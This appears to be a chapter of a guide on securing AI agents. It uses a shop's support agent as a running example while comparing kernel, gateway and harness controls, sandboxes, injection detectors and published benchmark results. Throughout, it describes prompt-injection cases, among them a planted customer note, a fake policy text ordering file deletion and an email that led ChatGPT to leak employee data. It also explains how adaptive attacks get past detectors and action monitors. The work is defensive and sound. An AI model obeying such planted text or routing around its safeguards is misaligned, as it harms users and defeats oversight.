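A hook may not cover everything the harness does. In the May 2026 version of OpenAI's *Hooks*, Codex runs the operator's check before file edits, MCP calls and simple shell commands, but not before web searches or some other shell commands. OpenAI calls the check "a guardrail rather than a complete enforcement boundary" because Codex can often do the same work through another tool. A mistake in the operator's code can also let a call through. If the code returns "ask", which this version doesn't support, Codex reports an error and runs the call anyway.

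### Fifteen paths and eight arrangements

Toyoda, Leung and U (2026), in *guardscope*, list 15 paths by which an agent's decision can take effect and work out which of them each kind of control would check. They compare eight arrangements:

- no control at all
- a gateway for remote tools
- the same gateway, with direct outbound connections blocked
- the same again, with tools on the local machine also routed through the gateway
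- the harness's own permission checks
- those permission checks plus a gateway
- a policy engine inside the harness process
- enforcement in the kernel

Here is their analysis for four of the arrangements:

| Kind of action | Gateway, remote tools only | Gateway for all tools, direct connections blocked | Harness checks | Kernel |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Call to a remote tool server | Checks | Checks | Checks | Checks |
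| Call to a tool server on the same machine (two paths) | Misses | Checks | Checks | Checks |
| Program that a tool starts and waits for | Misses | Misses | Checks | Checks |
| Tool that only changes data in the harness's memory | Misses | Misses | Checks | Misses |
| Direct network connection | Misses | Blocks | Misses | Checks |
| File or network operation by the harness's own code | Misses | Misses | Misses | Checks |
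| Request to a helper program on the same machine | Misses | Misses | Misses | Checks |
| Program that keeps running after the call has ended | Misses | Misses | Misses | Checks |
| Request from a tool server back to the harness | Misses | Misses | Misses | Checks |
| Job for a scheduler or similar service | Misses | Misses | Misses | Depends |
| Tool that calls another tool server | Depends | Depends | Misses | Checks |
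| Task for a sub-agent | Depends | Depends | Depends | Checks |
| Protocol request other than a tool call | Depends | Depends | Misses | Checks |
| Effect of the model's text without any tool call | Misses | Depends | Misses | Checks |

"Depends" means the outcome varies with the setup. For example, the harness's checks cover a sub-agent if they apply to it as they do to the main agent. Without kernel enforcement, every arrangement misses five kinds of action: operations by the harness's own code, requests to local helpers, programs that keep running after their tool call ends, requests from a tool server, and scheduled jobs. Adding a second control other than kernel enforcement doesn't help, because none of those controls is on the path these actions take. Even kernel enforcement catches scheduled jobs only if it also monitors the service that runs them.

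In the table, Toyoda and colleagues count a program that a tool starts as checked because the harness checks the command that launches it. This is a generous count, since the check doesn't cover what the program does afterwards. NVIDIA finds that the application loses control once such a program starts.

The support agent with its original three tools can take few of these paths. It has no shell, and if all its tools are remote, a gateway covers every call it can make. A coding agent that writes and runs programs can take most of these paths.

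### What happened when guardscope ran the controls

The second part of *guardscope* compares a control's own records with what the kernel observed:

1. The software sets up one of the eight arrangements, then sends an action that the policy must refuse. The test starts only if the control refuses it and records the refusal.
2. The harness replays 15 fixed actions. No language model is involved, so every run contains the same actions.
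3. A separate eBPF sensor called Tracee records what happens in the kernel.
4. The software matches the two sets of records. An action that took effect without a decision from the control counts as bypassed. A refusal counts only if the kernel shows no trace of the action.

The 15 actions cover only four of the 15 paths: remote tool calls, one kind of local tool call, direct network connections, and operations by the harness's own code. The rest of the table above, including every "depends", comes from analysis alone. Toyoda and colleagues drew up the list of paths in discussion with two AI models, and it may be incomplete.

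The runs confirmed the predictions for the gateways and the harness on the four paths. Toyoda and colleagues' gateway was the enforcement module of Microsoft's Agent Governance Toolkit, a free set of controls for agents. For the kernel, they used ActPlane, a research system.

| Arrangement | Remote tool calls | Local tool calls | Direct connections | Files, processes, credentials |
|---|---|---|---|---|
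| Microsoft's gateway | Checked | Missed | Missed | Missed |
| The same, direct connections blocked | Checked | Missed | Blocked | Missed |
| The same, local tools routed through it | Checked | Checked | Blocked | Missed |
| Harness checks plus Microsoft's gateway | Checked | Checked | Missed | Missed |
| ActPlane | Missed | Missed | One of two checked | Checked |

Microsoft (2026) advertises this module as intercepting every agent's action before execution. In the arrangement with both a gateway and harness checks, eight of the 15 actions took effect without any policy decision. Microsoft's *Known Limitations & Design Boundaries* describes the toolkit more modestly as application-layer software and recommends combining it with containers and network policies. It also warns that the toolkit allows every action if nobody has loaded a policy, even though the dashboard may show the agent as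 governed. The first step of guardscope's procedure would detect this mistake, and an operator can copy it by sending a forbidden test call each time the agent starts.

ActPlane checked seven of the 15 actions and missed the other eight, including all seven tool calls. A kernel control covers only the kinds of request it has checks for, so it can miss actions that its position in the kernel would let it catch. Together, ActPlane and the harness checks would have covered 14 of the 15 actions, all except one network message of a type that ActPlane doesn't monitor. Toyoda and colleagues recommend such combinations but did not run this one.

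These results show only whether a control examined an action, not whether it would have decided correctly or how often a real agent takes a path that the control misses.

### Following an action into the kernel

*ActPlane* (Zheng, Wu and colleagues, 2026) reports that kernel checks also caught more rule violations than checks on tool calls did in its developers' own test. The system uses information-flow labels, as FIDES does, but attaches them to programs, files and network addresses. A program that reads a file of passwords acquires that file's label, as does any program it starts, and a rule can then block them from making outside connections. Rules can also cover the order of events, such as blocking a commit to a code repository unless the tests have passed since the last edit.

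A test of ActPlane used 38 rules from real software projects and 190 recorded sessions, 114 of which broke a rule. Some broke it through an ordinary tool call, and others through a script or a file that looked harmless. ActPlane detected 77% of the violations. Three systems that check tool calls detected 34–40%, and almost none of the violations in harmless-looking files. All the systems did about equally well on violations through ordinary tool calls, so the overall gap depends on how many indirect violations the developers included.

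ActPlane also intervened wrongly in 18 of the 76 sessions that followed the rules, mostly because a model had written the rule too broadly. When ActPlane explained its refusals, the agent went on to comply after 98% of detections, compared with 31% when ActPlane returned only a generic error.

ActPlane slowed a replay of an agent's work by 1.9% with 32 active rules. The slowdown stayed below 8.4% with up to 100 rules, even during a Linux kernel build, which starts far more programs than an agent normally does.

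ActPlane could stop a report script that had opened the customer file from connecting to the internet, but it couldn't determine whether the script was sending addresses or a sales total, because it doesn't read file contents. The same rule wouldn't work for the harness, which has to read customer records and then contact the mail server.

### Personal data that bypasses tokenization

The same reasoning applies to PII tokenization. In Anthropic's sketch, the MCP client replaces personal values, so data that reaches the model by another route stays as it is:

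| Route | What happens |
|---|---|
| File | The harness's own file tool reads a customer list without going through the MCP client |
| Screenshot | The address is part of an image, and a text detector finds no text to search |
| Log | A shell command prints an error message with a customer's address in it |
| Other tool | A tool connected through separate code returns a record directly |

MCP also has ways to get text to the model other than tool results. The client can fetch a document as a "resource", and a tool server can ask the harness to run the model on text it supplies. Toyoda and colleagues list both among the paths that a control on tool calls can miss. If the shop attached its detector only to tool results, it would miss personal data on these routes too.

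A sandbox doesn't stop the files Claude reads from going to the model's provider, as Anthropic notes in its guide to sandbox environments.

Data reaches the provider in a prompt however it enters the conversation, so the shop can run the detector again on the connection to the provider, before each prompt leaves. This second pass would catch the address from the log and the customer list. It would need software that reads text in images to catch the screenshot. The shop still needs the first pass, because the harness can use a record's labelled fields, and store which customer each value belongs to, only when the record arrives. The shop also has to block every other connection to the provider, or a plugin could send a prompt that skips the second pass.

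### Closing the routes around the scanner

Operators can close many of these routes with limits on what the agent's programs can reach. NVIDIA's *Four Ways to Deploy More Secure AI Agents* summarizes six months of tests in which the company's AI Red Team, its in-house attackers, tried to misuse agents. Where they succeeded, they typically found the same four failures:

1. People who had no business with the agent could give it instructions. Several agents held one employee's credentials and answered anyone on the internal network.
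2. The agent had tools that could run arbitrary code.
3. Nothing limited its outbound connections.
4. It could read passwords and access keys in plain text.

NVIDIA lists four failures but doesn't report how many agents it tested or how often each failure occurred. The first lets an attacker reach the agent, and the other three provide ways around a scanner. Most teams had relied on instructions to the model, sometimes with a second model as judge, and the testers routinely bypassed both with prompts.

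The best remedy for the second failure is to give the agent no shell. If the agent needs one, it should run in a sandbox. Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts* (2025) argues that a sandbox has to restrict both files and the network. With open network access, a misled agent can send out whatever it is allowed to read, and with unrestricted file access, it can change files that let it escape the sandbox. NVIDIA adds that the agent must not be able to edit its own configuration files, because other programs may later run commands from them outside the sandbox.

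*Toward Securing AI Agents Like Operating Systems* (2026) points out that a sandbox protects completely only if it covers every relevant effect. Claude Code's built-in sandbox restricts shell commands, but the file tools, MCP servers and hooks run outside it. An operator who wants to sandbox those too has to run all of Claude Code in a container, a virtual machine or Anthropic's separate sandbox software.

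To address the third failure, NVIDIA recommends blocking all outbound connections except those on a short list. The shop's list would contain the model's provider, the customer database, the payment system and the mail server. When an agent had such limits, the testers had to carry out every step through the agent, which was slower and less reliable than controlling the machine directly.

*Sandlock* (2026) observes that a list of allowed addresses is necessary but not sufficient, because an agent permitted to reach a legitimate service can also reach an attacker's endpoints through the same IP address. The shop's mail server poses a similar problem, since it will deliver to strangers as well as to Keller. *Sandlock* proposes splitting the task, as the Dual LLM pattern does, so that only a stage that never receives untrusted text has network access. The rule on permitted recipients is still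 necessary.

Credentials are probably the most useful of these limits for a scanner. If the support agent's report script could read the payment system's access key, it could issue a refund without calling `refund.issue`. If only the gateway holds the key, the payment system rejects any request that didn't come through the gateway, even one sent by a route nobody has thought of. Anthropic uses this design for code repositories in its cloud service. The sandbox has only a limited credential, and a proxy outside it checks each request, for example to confirm that the code is going to the permitted branch. The proxy then adds the real credential.

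The key has to stay out of the sandbox altogether. When outbound limits prevented the testers from sending credentials over the network, they persuaded agents to print the credentials in the chat instead.

### The cost of these limits

Someone has to set up the limits and keep them current. Anthropic's sandbox software blocks the network by default, so the operator has to list the domains and folders each task needs. If the settings file is missing, the software starts anyway with its strict defaults, so a successful start doesn't prove that it loaded the operator's settings. On Linux, it selects which configuration files to protect at launch and doesn't cover repositories the agent creates later. Kernel controls can be even harder to install. ActPlane ran on only one of the three kernel versions Toyoda and colleagues tried.

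In return, users face fewer interruptions. Anthropic's staff received 84% fewer permission requests with the sandbox, because the agent could work freely inside it.

The limits also stop agents from completing some tasks. *Permission Denied* (Davidovich, Amar and colleagues, 2026) tested 12 coding agents on 89 command-line tasks. The strictest setting allowed connections only to about 200 listed domains, made system folders read-only and removed administrator rights. Under it, the agents' success rates fell by 7.1 to 18.3 percentage points, and the average cost of a task rose by 16% to 167%. Grok 4.5 had the smallest drop in success rate but the largest rise in cost.

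Seven of the 89 tasks became impossible, only one of them purely because of the network limits. On the other 82, the average success rate fell from 72.5% to 65.1%. Removing administrator rights caused most of that drop, lowering the rate to 66.9% on its own. The network and file limits, together with a stricter lock on privileges, lowered it by only another 1.8 points.

Agents rarely gave up when they hit a limit. On two tasks Davidovich and colleagues examined closely, the median cost roughly tripled, almost always because the agent built a workaround, such as compiling a program it could not download. Runs that hit the network limit did so about ten times on average. An operator who treats every refused connection as a sign of an attack will therefore get many false alarms from agents just trying to finish their work.

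The study measured how much the limits reduced agents' success on coding tasks, but not how much security they provide. Davidovich and colleagues found that they could predict the losses by replaying each task's reference solution under the strict setting. On the 50 tasks where the solution still worked, the agents' success rate hardly changed, from 73.8% to 71.8%. On the 32 where they had to write a new solution, it fell from 70.3% to 54.5%. The shop could predict its own losses by replaying the tool calls from last month's tickets on a test system before it turns the limits on.

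## How the safeguards fare against prompt injection

The stranger's note is on Maria Keller's record, so the model reads it whenever `crm.lookup` returns that record, even if the operator has closed the routes around the scanner. The operator can add a screen that checks each tool result for planted instructions before the model reads it. If the screen misses the note and the model follows its instructions, the scanner may still stop the resulting call.

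### Screening tool results

Claude Code's auto mode includes such a screen, which Anthropic calls a probe. It runs on Anthropic's servers and examines file contents, web pages, shell output and responses from external tools. When content looks like an attempt to hijack the agent, the probe leaves it in place and adds a warning that it is suspect and that the agent should stick to what the user asked for. The shop's model would still receive the price of the kettle, along with a warning about the note.

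A false alarm does little harm in this design because the agent loses no data, but the warning works only if the model acts on it. Anthropic's two articles on auto mode give no error rates for the probe alone.

Developers can add a similar check to their own agents with OpenAI's Guardrails software. OpenAI's *Prompt Injection Detection* explains that the check runs on each proposed tool call and again on each tool result. A language model, by default GPT-4.1 mini, compares the call or result with the user's goal and rates its confidence, from 0 to 1, that the two don't match. The check flags anything that scores above the operator's threshold. If a user asks about the weather in Tokyo and the agent also proposes a bank transfer, the check flags the call. If the weather tool returns a bank balance along with the temperature, the check flags the result.

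The check on results might cause trouble for the shop. Keller's record contains her husband's phone number, which has nothing to do with a cracked lid, so the check may treat it as unrelated private data.

OpenAI's published results also depend heavily on the test set. An earlier version of OpenAI's *Prompt Injection Detection* reports that the default model caught 98.6% of attacks at a false-positive rate of 1%, on 1,000 samples that OpenAI generated itself. The newer version uses 1,486 attack samples, most from the benchmark AgentDojo, and reports a detection rate of 0% at the same false-positive rate.

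The 0% overstates the problem because it measures recall with no false alarms allowed. The new set has only 97 harmless samples, so even one false alarm would exceed the 1% limit, and at least one harmless sample scored as high as any attack. The precision figures on the same page imply that the default model can catch 95% of the attacks with about two false alarms among the 97. But all 949 AgentDojo attacks use the same template, so the result is weak evidence about attacks that are worded differently.

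### Fifteen detectors on harmless results

Many operators use a small classifier instead of a language model, and choose it by its benchmark score. *Passing the Test You Trained On* (Liu, 2026) examines whether such scores predict how a detector behaves inside an agent. Liu replayed the correct tool calls for every task in two benchmarks, without any model, so the tool results were certain to be harmless. Liu then planted attacks in the data and replayed the same calls, so any result that changed contained an attack.

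One benchmark was AgentDojo. The other, τ-bench, simulates customer service for a retailer and an airline, so it is closer to the shop's work. Liu also used BIPIA, an older collection of emails, tables and code with inserted attacks. These are his results for six of the fifteen detectors. The false alarms are at each detector's default threshold, and the catch rates are at a threshold that allows 1% false alarms:

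| Detector | False alarms, AgentDojo | False alarms, τ-bench | Caught, AgentDojo | Caught, τ-bench | Caught, BIPIA |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Horizon-Labs | 0.0% | 0.7% | 82.2% | 100.0% | 37.7% |
| Wolf Defender | 0.9% | 0.0% | 73.8% | 90.8% | 3.5% |
| Prompt Guard 2 (larger version) | 0.6% | 0.0% | 69.4% | 57.9% | 10.4% |
| Prismor | 6.5% | 46.2% | 72.2% | 15.2% | 4.0% |
| PIGuard | 29.5% | 11.0% | 2.1% | 52.7% | 95.1% |
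| ProtectAI v2 | 30.1% | 66.9% | 0.5% | 10.1% | 0.7% |

PIGuard is the best of the fifteen on BIPIA but among the worst on AgentDojo. It gave the message "Password updated" the maximum score of 1.00. If the harness dropped every result that PIGuard flagged, about 60% of AgentDojo's tasks would lose at least one harmless result.

Liu traces the difference to training data. PIGuard's developers had trained it on 1,116 inputs from BIPIA and on 53 of the 62 attack texts that he planted in τ-bench, though those 53 were in the training data as short prompts rather than inside tool results. PIGuard caught 52.1% of the tool results containing one of those 53 attacks and 55.8% of those containing one of the others, so training on an attack's text didn't help when the surrounding text was new. Horizon-Labs, whose developers trained it on instructions planted in documents and tool responses, did best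 on both agent benchmarks. Liu found none of the benchmarks' attacks in the parts of Horizon-Labs's training data that he could check.

False-alarm rates carried over between the two agent benchmarks much better than catch rates did. The shop can therefore get a useful estimate of a detector's false-alarm rate by running it on last month's customer records, which costs little and requires no attacks. It might also reduce false alarms by sending the detector only the text of the `note` field. When Liu removed the field names from AgentDojo's tool results, PIGuard's false-alarm rate fell from 20.0% to 6.7%, and it caught about as many attacks as before at its default threshold.

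### Why two layers can fail together

Anthropic argues that the probe and the check on calls "compound". An attack has to get past the probe and then make the agent propose a call that a second model classifies as safe and in line with the user's request. The second model is never given the attacker's text. Defeating both layers is harder than defeating either alone, but how much harder depends on whether the same attacks defeat both.

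If the screen misses 10% of attacks and the call check misses 10%, it is tempting to multiply the two and expect 1% to get through. The correct formula is

P(both miss) = P(screen misses) × P(call check misses, given that the screen missed)

The second factor equals the call check's ordinary miss rate only if the two kinds of miss are independent. Suppose that nine in ten attacks are crude and the rest are skilled, and that the layers have these invented miss rates:

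| Attacks | Share | Screen misses | Call check misses | Both miss |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Crude | 90% | 2% | 5% | 0.1% |
| Skilled | 10% | 90% | 80% | 72% |
| All | 100% | 10.8% | 12.5% | 7.3% |

Multiplying the two layers' average failure rates gives 1.4%, but 7.3% of the attacks get through both layers, and nearly all of those are skilled attacks. An attacker who can write skilled attacks will use only those, and the two layers together fail to stop 72% of them.

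An attacker can defeat both layers with text that doesn't look like an instruction but leads to a call that resembles the user's request. The stranger could word his note as a routine entry saying that the customer has a new email address. A screen for commands would have nothing to flag. The agent would then send the refund confirmation to the new address, and the call would look to a reviewing model like an email about a refund that Keller requested.

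The shop's rule on permitted recipients would still block this email, because it checks only the address. A second layer helps most when it relies on facts that the attacker can't influence. Two language models that both look for suspicious intent are more likely to miss the same attacks.

### AgentDojo as a test

Most published figures for these defences come from AgentDojo, a benchmark that simulates inboxes, bank accounts and chat channels. These contain marked places where outsiders could plausibly write, such as the body of an email or the text of a file. The benchmark inserts an attack there and lets the agent work on an ordinary task. *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (2026) explains that code, rather than a model, then decides whether the attack succeeded, for example by checking whether money left the account.

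The original *AgentDojo* (2024) combined its 97 tasks with attackers' goals to make 629 test cases. Later work reports more than 900 cases, presumably from a newer version. The paper described its attacks as relatively simple and expressed the hope that others would add better ones, but many evaluations have used the built-in attacks unchanged.

A static test uses a fixed list of attacks. It takes few resources to run and is repeatable, but it only shows whether a defence stops an attacker who copies published text, not one who rewrites the text after it fails. In an adaptive test, the attacker keeps revising the attack until it gets past the defence or the budget runs out.

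### The attacker moves second

In *The Attacker Moves Second* (2025), Nasr, Carlini and colleagues from OpenAI, Anthropic, Google DeepMind and other institutions tested twelve published defences with adaptive attacks. They report success rates above 90% against most of the defences, although the majority of the original papers had reported rates near zero.

All the automated attacks follow the same loop. The attacker proposes some texts, tries them on the defended system, scores the outcomes and uses the scores to write the next batch. One version uses the model's internals to compute which changes to the text would help. Another trains a language model to write attacks, rewarding it for successes. A third keeps the best texts and has a language model vary them. Nasr and colleagues also ran a competition in which more than 500 people attacked some of the defences by hand.

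They chose whichever method seemed most likely to work against each defence:

| Kind of defence | Defence | Result of adaptive attacks |
|---|---|---|
| Wording or layout of the prompt | Spotlighting, Prompt Sandwiching | Over 95% succeeded |
| | RPO | 96–98% succeeded |
| Training the model to resist | Circuit Breakers | 100% succeeded |
| | StruQ | Succeeded in every case tested |
| | MetaSecAlign | 96% succeeded |
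| Separate detector | Protect AI, PromptGuard, Model Armor | Over 90% succeeded |
| | PIGuard | 71% succeeded |
| Hidden test of the input | Data Sentinel | Bypassed in every case |
| | MELON | 76% succeeded, or 95% when the attacker knew the design |

RPO and Circuit Breakers matter less here because they are meant to stop users from obtaining forbidden content. MetaSecAlign's results contrast most clearly with static testing, in which only 2% of AgentDojo's fixed attacks had succeeded against it.

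Of the twelve defenses, MELON comes closest to checking tool calls. It runs the agent a second time with the user's request replaced by a request to summarize the tool results. If the same tool calls appear again, the tool results must have caused them, since the second run doesn't include the user's request. Attackers who knew this wrote injections that made the agent behave differently in the two runs.

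Many of the texts that got past the detectors looked harmless and didn't openly try to override the user's request. One told the agent that company policy required deleting a certain file whenever a meeting was rescheduled. A detector that flagged such texts would also flag more harmless ones. Combining several detectors didn't stop Nasr and colleagues either, as one would expect if the detectors share weaknesses. The researchers consider detectors a limited but useful component, because they stop unsophisticated attacks with little overhead.

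These attackers had ample computing power, and the automated search against the detectors could see each detector's confidence score. The stranger lacks that computing power, and the shop's software wouldn't show him a score, but he could download an open detector such as PIGuard and practise on his own computer. The competition's results also need caution, because a scenario counted as broken if any one participant broke it. By that count, the participants broke every scenario in a subset where the automated search succeeded in 69%.

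*The Attacker Moves Second* is strong evidence against relying on a screen. It is only indirect evidence about scanners, because none of the twelve defences it tests is a fixed rule on tool calls or a reviewer that compares each call with the user's request, as auto mode does.

### Adaptive attacks on checks of tool calls

*Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (2026) proposes testing checks on actions against an attacker who knows the policy. The attacker can revise the injected text to get past the deployed check, forge the labels that record where data came from, persuade the person who approves doubtful calls, or leak information through permitted behaviour. According to the paper, it was still unknown whether systems such as Progent and CaMeL would withstand a strong attack of this kind.

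*AutoDojo* (Ma, Li and colleagues, 2026) gives a partial answer. It is an adaptive version of AgentDojo, used to test ten defences with five models. The attacker is much weaker than those of Nasr and colleagues. It doesn't know which defence is installed and learns only how often its text succeeded. Gemini 3.1 Pro reads the earlier attempts with their scores, guesses why they failed and writes a new one. After six rounds, only the most successful text counts towards the results. That text has to work on agents that read the same page or message while doing different tasks, because a real attacker doesn't know what the user will ask for.

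With GPT-4o mini as the agent, these shares of attacks succeeded:

| Defence | How it works | Fixed attack | Adaptive attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| PIGuard | Detects injections in tool results | 0.0% | 28.0% |
| DataFilter | Removes injections from tool results | 12.6% | 33.4% |
| ProtectAI | Detects injections in tool results | 7.2% | 15.4% |
| DRIFT | Restricts calls to a plan, with a model that looks for conflicting instructions | 2.6% | 6.4% |

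Without any defence, 52.4% of the adaptive attacks succeeded. With Progent, which checks tool calls against a policy written for the task, 7.7% succeeded. CaMeL and a newer system called ROPE track where each value came from, so rewording an attack doesn't affect them as long as their policies are correct. Some of the same researchers worked on ROPE.

Liu's measurements help explain PIGuard's 0.0% on the fixed attack. At its default threshold, PIGuard flags almost a third of AgentDojo's harmless results, so it blocks much of what the agent needs along with the attacks. Ma and colleagues found that PIGuard and ProtectAI reduced the share of tasks completed by a quarter to a half on every model, while Progent reduced it by at most 7 percentage points. CaMeL was the most effective defence overall but reduced usefulness the most on four of the five models.

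How precisely the user states the task also matters. Ma and colleagues sorted the tasks into three groups. In the first, the user gives the action and all its details, such as a new postal address. In the second, the user names the action but the agent has to look up a detail, as when it is asked to pay the bill in a certain file. In the third, the user asks the agent to carry out whatever actions the material specifies, such as everything on a to-do list. Against PIGuard with GPT-4o mini, 17.3% of adaptive attacks succeeded in the first group and 54.2% in the third. When the agent is supposed to take its instructions from a text, an injected instruction can look like one of them.

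With Progent, DRIFT and ROPE, the rate was at most 11% in every group. For many of the open-ended tasks, Progent and DRIFT permit only tools that read data, so a planted request to pay someone fails however it is worded.

The shop's support agent belongs in the third group. Its task is to handle whatever customers request in their tickets, so the customer decides whether it gives a refund, a replacement or an answer. Screening for suspicious wording works least well for this kind of agent, and limits on amounts and recipients matter most.

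Ma and colleagues' results also show why a low attack success rate may have nothing to do with the defence. The fixed attack succeeded in only 0.3% of cases on Claude Haiku 4.5 without any protection, so even an ineffective defence would appear nearly perfect on that model.

### The Trajectory Labs test

This is the main difficulty with the most impressive result for a deployed scanner. Anthropic commissioned Trajectory Labs to test the versions of Claude Code and Codex available on 17 July 2026. The testers tried 72 injection scenarios that Anthropic hadn't seen, ten times each. Outside the test, a successful attack would have caused irreversible harm, such as stolen data or a fraudulent payment.

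| Agent | Without the scanner | With the scanner |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Code with Fable 5, Opus 5 or Sonnet 5 | 0.09% on average | 0% |
| Codex with GPT-5.6 Sol | 19.03% | 5.83% |

With auto mode on, none of the 720 attempts against each of the three Claude models succeeded. But if the 0.09% success rate without auto mode is the average for these three models, it equals only about two successes in 2,160 attempts. The models already ignored nearly every attack, which left the scanner almost nothing to stop, so the test provides little evidence of how much the scanner helped.

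The *Ajar* test comes closer to testing the scanner on its own, because it gave auto mode calls as if the agent had already fallen for the attack. Auto mode would have allowed some of them. The test's set-up was imperfect, but the result suggests that auto mode would stop fewer attacks if the agent's model were easier to fool.

The Codex figures are more informative about a scanner's contribution. They correspond to 137 successful attempts without Auto-review and 42 with it, a reduction of about 70%. Some of this reduction may be due to the sandbox, because the comparison was with Full Access mode, which probably turns off the sandbox as well as Auto-review.

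The test also used the same static attacks against every model. They had been tuned on an older model, Claude Opus 4.7, and nobody revised them when they failed against the newer ones. Attackers who adapted to their target would presumably succeed more often than the 0% measured for Opus 5 with auto mode and the 5.83% for GPT-5.6 Sol. Anthropic notes that OpenAI released a new version of Auto-review after the test, and that both agents used a browser connection built by Trajectory Labs, without the safeguards in the companies' own browser products.

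The 720 attempts also provide less evidence than 720 different attacks would, because attempts at the same scenario tend to succeed or fail together. VentureBeat reports that a single attempt succeeded 17.8% of the time against Claude Opus 4.6, a February 2026 model that Anthropic has since replaced, when it operated a graphical interface without safeguards. If attempts were independent, ten of them would have an 86% chance of at least one success, and 200 would be practically certain to succeed at least once. The measured rate after 200 attempts was 78.6%, so some attacks must have kept failing however often the testers repeated them. With safeguards, the rate after 200 attempts was still 57.1%.

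If the 72 scenarios are treated as the real sample, zero successes are compatible with a true rate of up to about 4% of scenarios, since

(1 − 0.04)⁷² ≈ 0.05

Even if one scenario in 25 could defeat the agent, a test of this size would find no such scenario about 5% of the time.

Other results confirm that recent models differ greatly in their own resistance. Anthropic's system card for Opus 5 reports a browser test without safeguards in which the attack success rate was 31.5% for Opus 4.8, 29.7% for Mythos 5, 3.70% for Opus 5 and 0.93% for Sonnet 5, all with extended thinking. The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* reports that no attack succeeded against Opus 5 in 129 scenarios in Anthropic's own browser software. For the shop, the choice of model may therefore matter as much as the choice of scanner. The shop should also repeat its tests when it changes models,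 because a newer model isn't necessarily more resistant. Opus 5 came out after Sonnet 5 but did worse in the test without safeguards.

In August 2026, soon after the 0% result, the security researcher Johann Rehberger challenged it by reporting an attack on auto mode with Opus 5 that he claims works 80% of the time (Willison, 2026, *Breaking Claude Code Opus 5 Auto Mode*).

### Injections on public web pages

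Google's *AI threats in the wild* (2026) looked for actual prompt injection attempts, rather than testing what attackers could do, by searching Common Crawl, an archive that copies two to three billion web pages a month. The researchers first searched for typical phrases, such as commands to ignore earlier instructions. They then used Google's model Gemini to assess whether each suspicious passage fitted the rest of its page, and people checked the results.

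Most of the initial matches were harmless examples quoted in articles and research papers about prompt injection. A screen would also raise false alarms when an agent reads such articles for its user.

The genuine injections were mostly unsophisticated. Some were pranks that told AI assistants to change their tone. Some website owners asked assistants to add useful context to a summary or to recommend their business over others. Others tried to keep agents away, in one case by luring them to a page that never finishes loading. A few injections were attempts to steal data or delete the user's files, and most of these looked like experiments by individuals. Google found no significant use of the advanced techniques that researchers published in 2025.

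Google reports that malicious injections rose by 32% between November 2025 and February 2026, but doesn't say how many there were, so the increase may be from a very small base. The search looked only for known phrases on public pages and left out most social media. It also didn't cover email or customer records, the texts that matter to the shop. It counted planted texts whether or not an agent had obeyed them.

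### A data theft from ChatGPT

The best-known cases of agents obeying such texts are still demonstrations by researchers, as Sophos notes in SC Media. One was an attack on a deployed product, ChatGPT. OpenAI's *Designing agents to resist prompt injection* says outside researchers reported it to the company in 2025. A user asks ChatGPT to research the day's emails. One email, worded like a routine business message, says that the assistant is authorized to look up employee profiles and should submit an employee's name and address to a compliance system. The attacker owns the address given for that system. In testing, the attack worked half the time.

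A screen for suspicious instructions could easily have missed this email, since it resembles the policy notice that a detector missed in Nasr and colleagues' tests. A model reviewing the resulting call might also have approved it, because the user had asked for wide-ranging research and looking something up in an outside system fits that request.

A fixed list of permitted destinations would have blocked the transfer. Such a list suits the shop's support agent, which needs to reach only a few systems, but not a research assistant, which has to open pages that nobody has listed in advance.

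For such an assistant, PII tokenization would have been the better safeguard. If the harness had replaced the employee's name and address with placeholders before the model read the emails, and had a rule never to restore real values for web requests, the attacker would have received `[NAME_1]` and `[ADDRESS_1]`. This depends on both the detector finding the two values and the rule against restoring them. A harness that restored placeholders for any permitted tool would have sent the attacker the real name and address.
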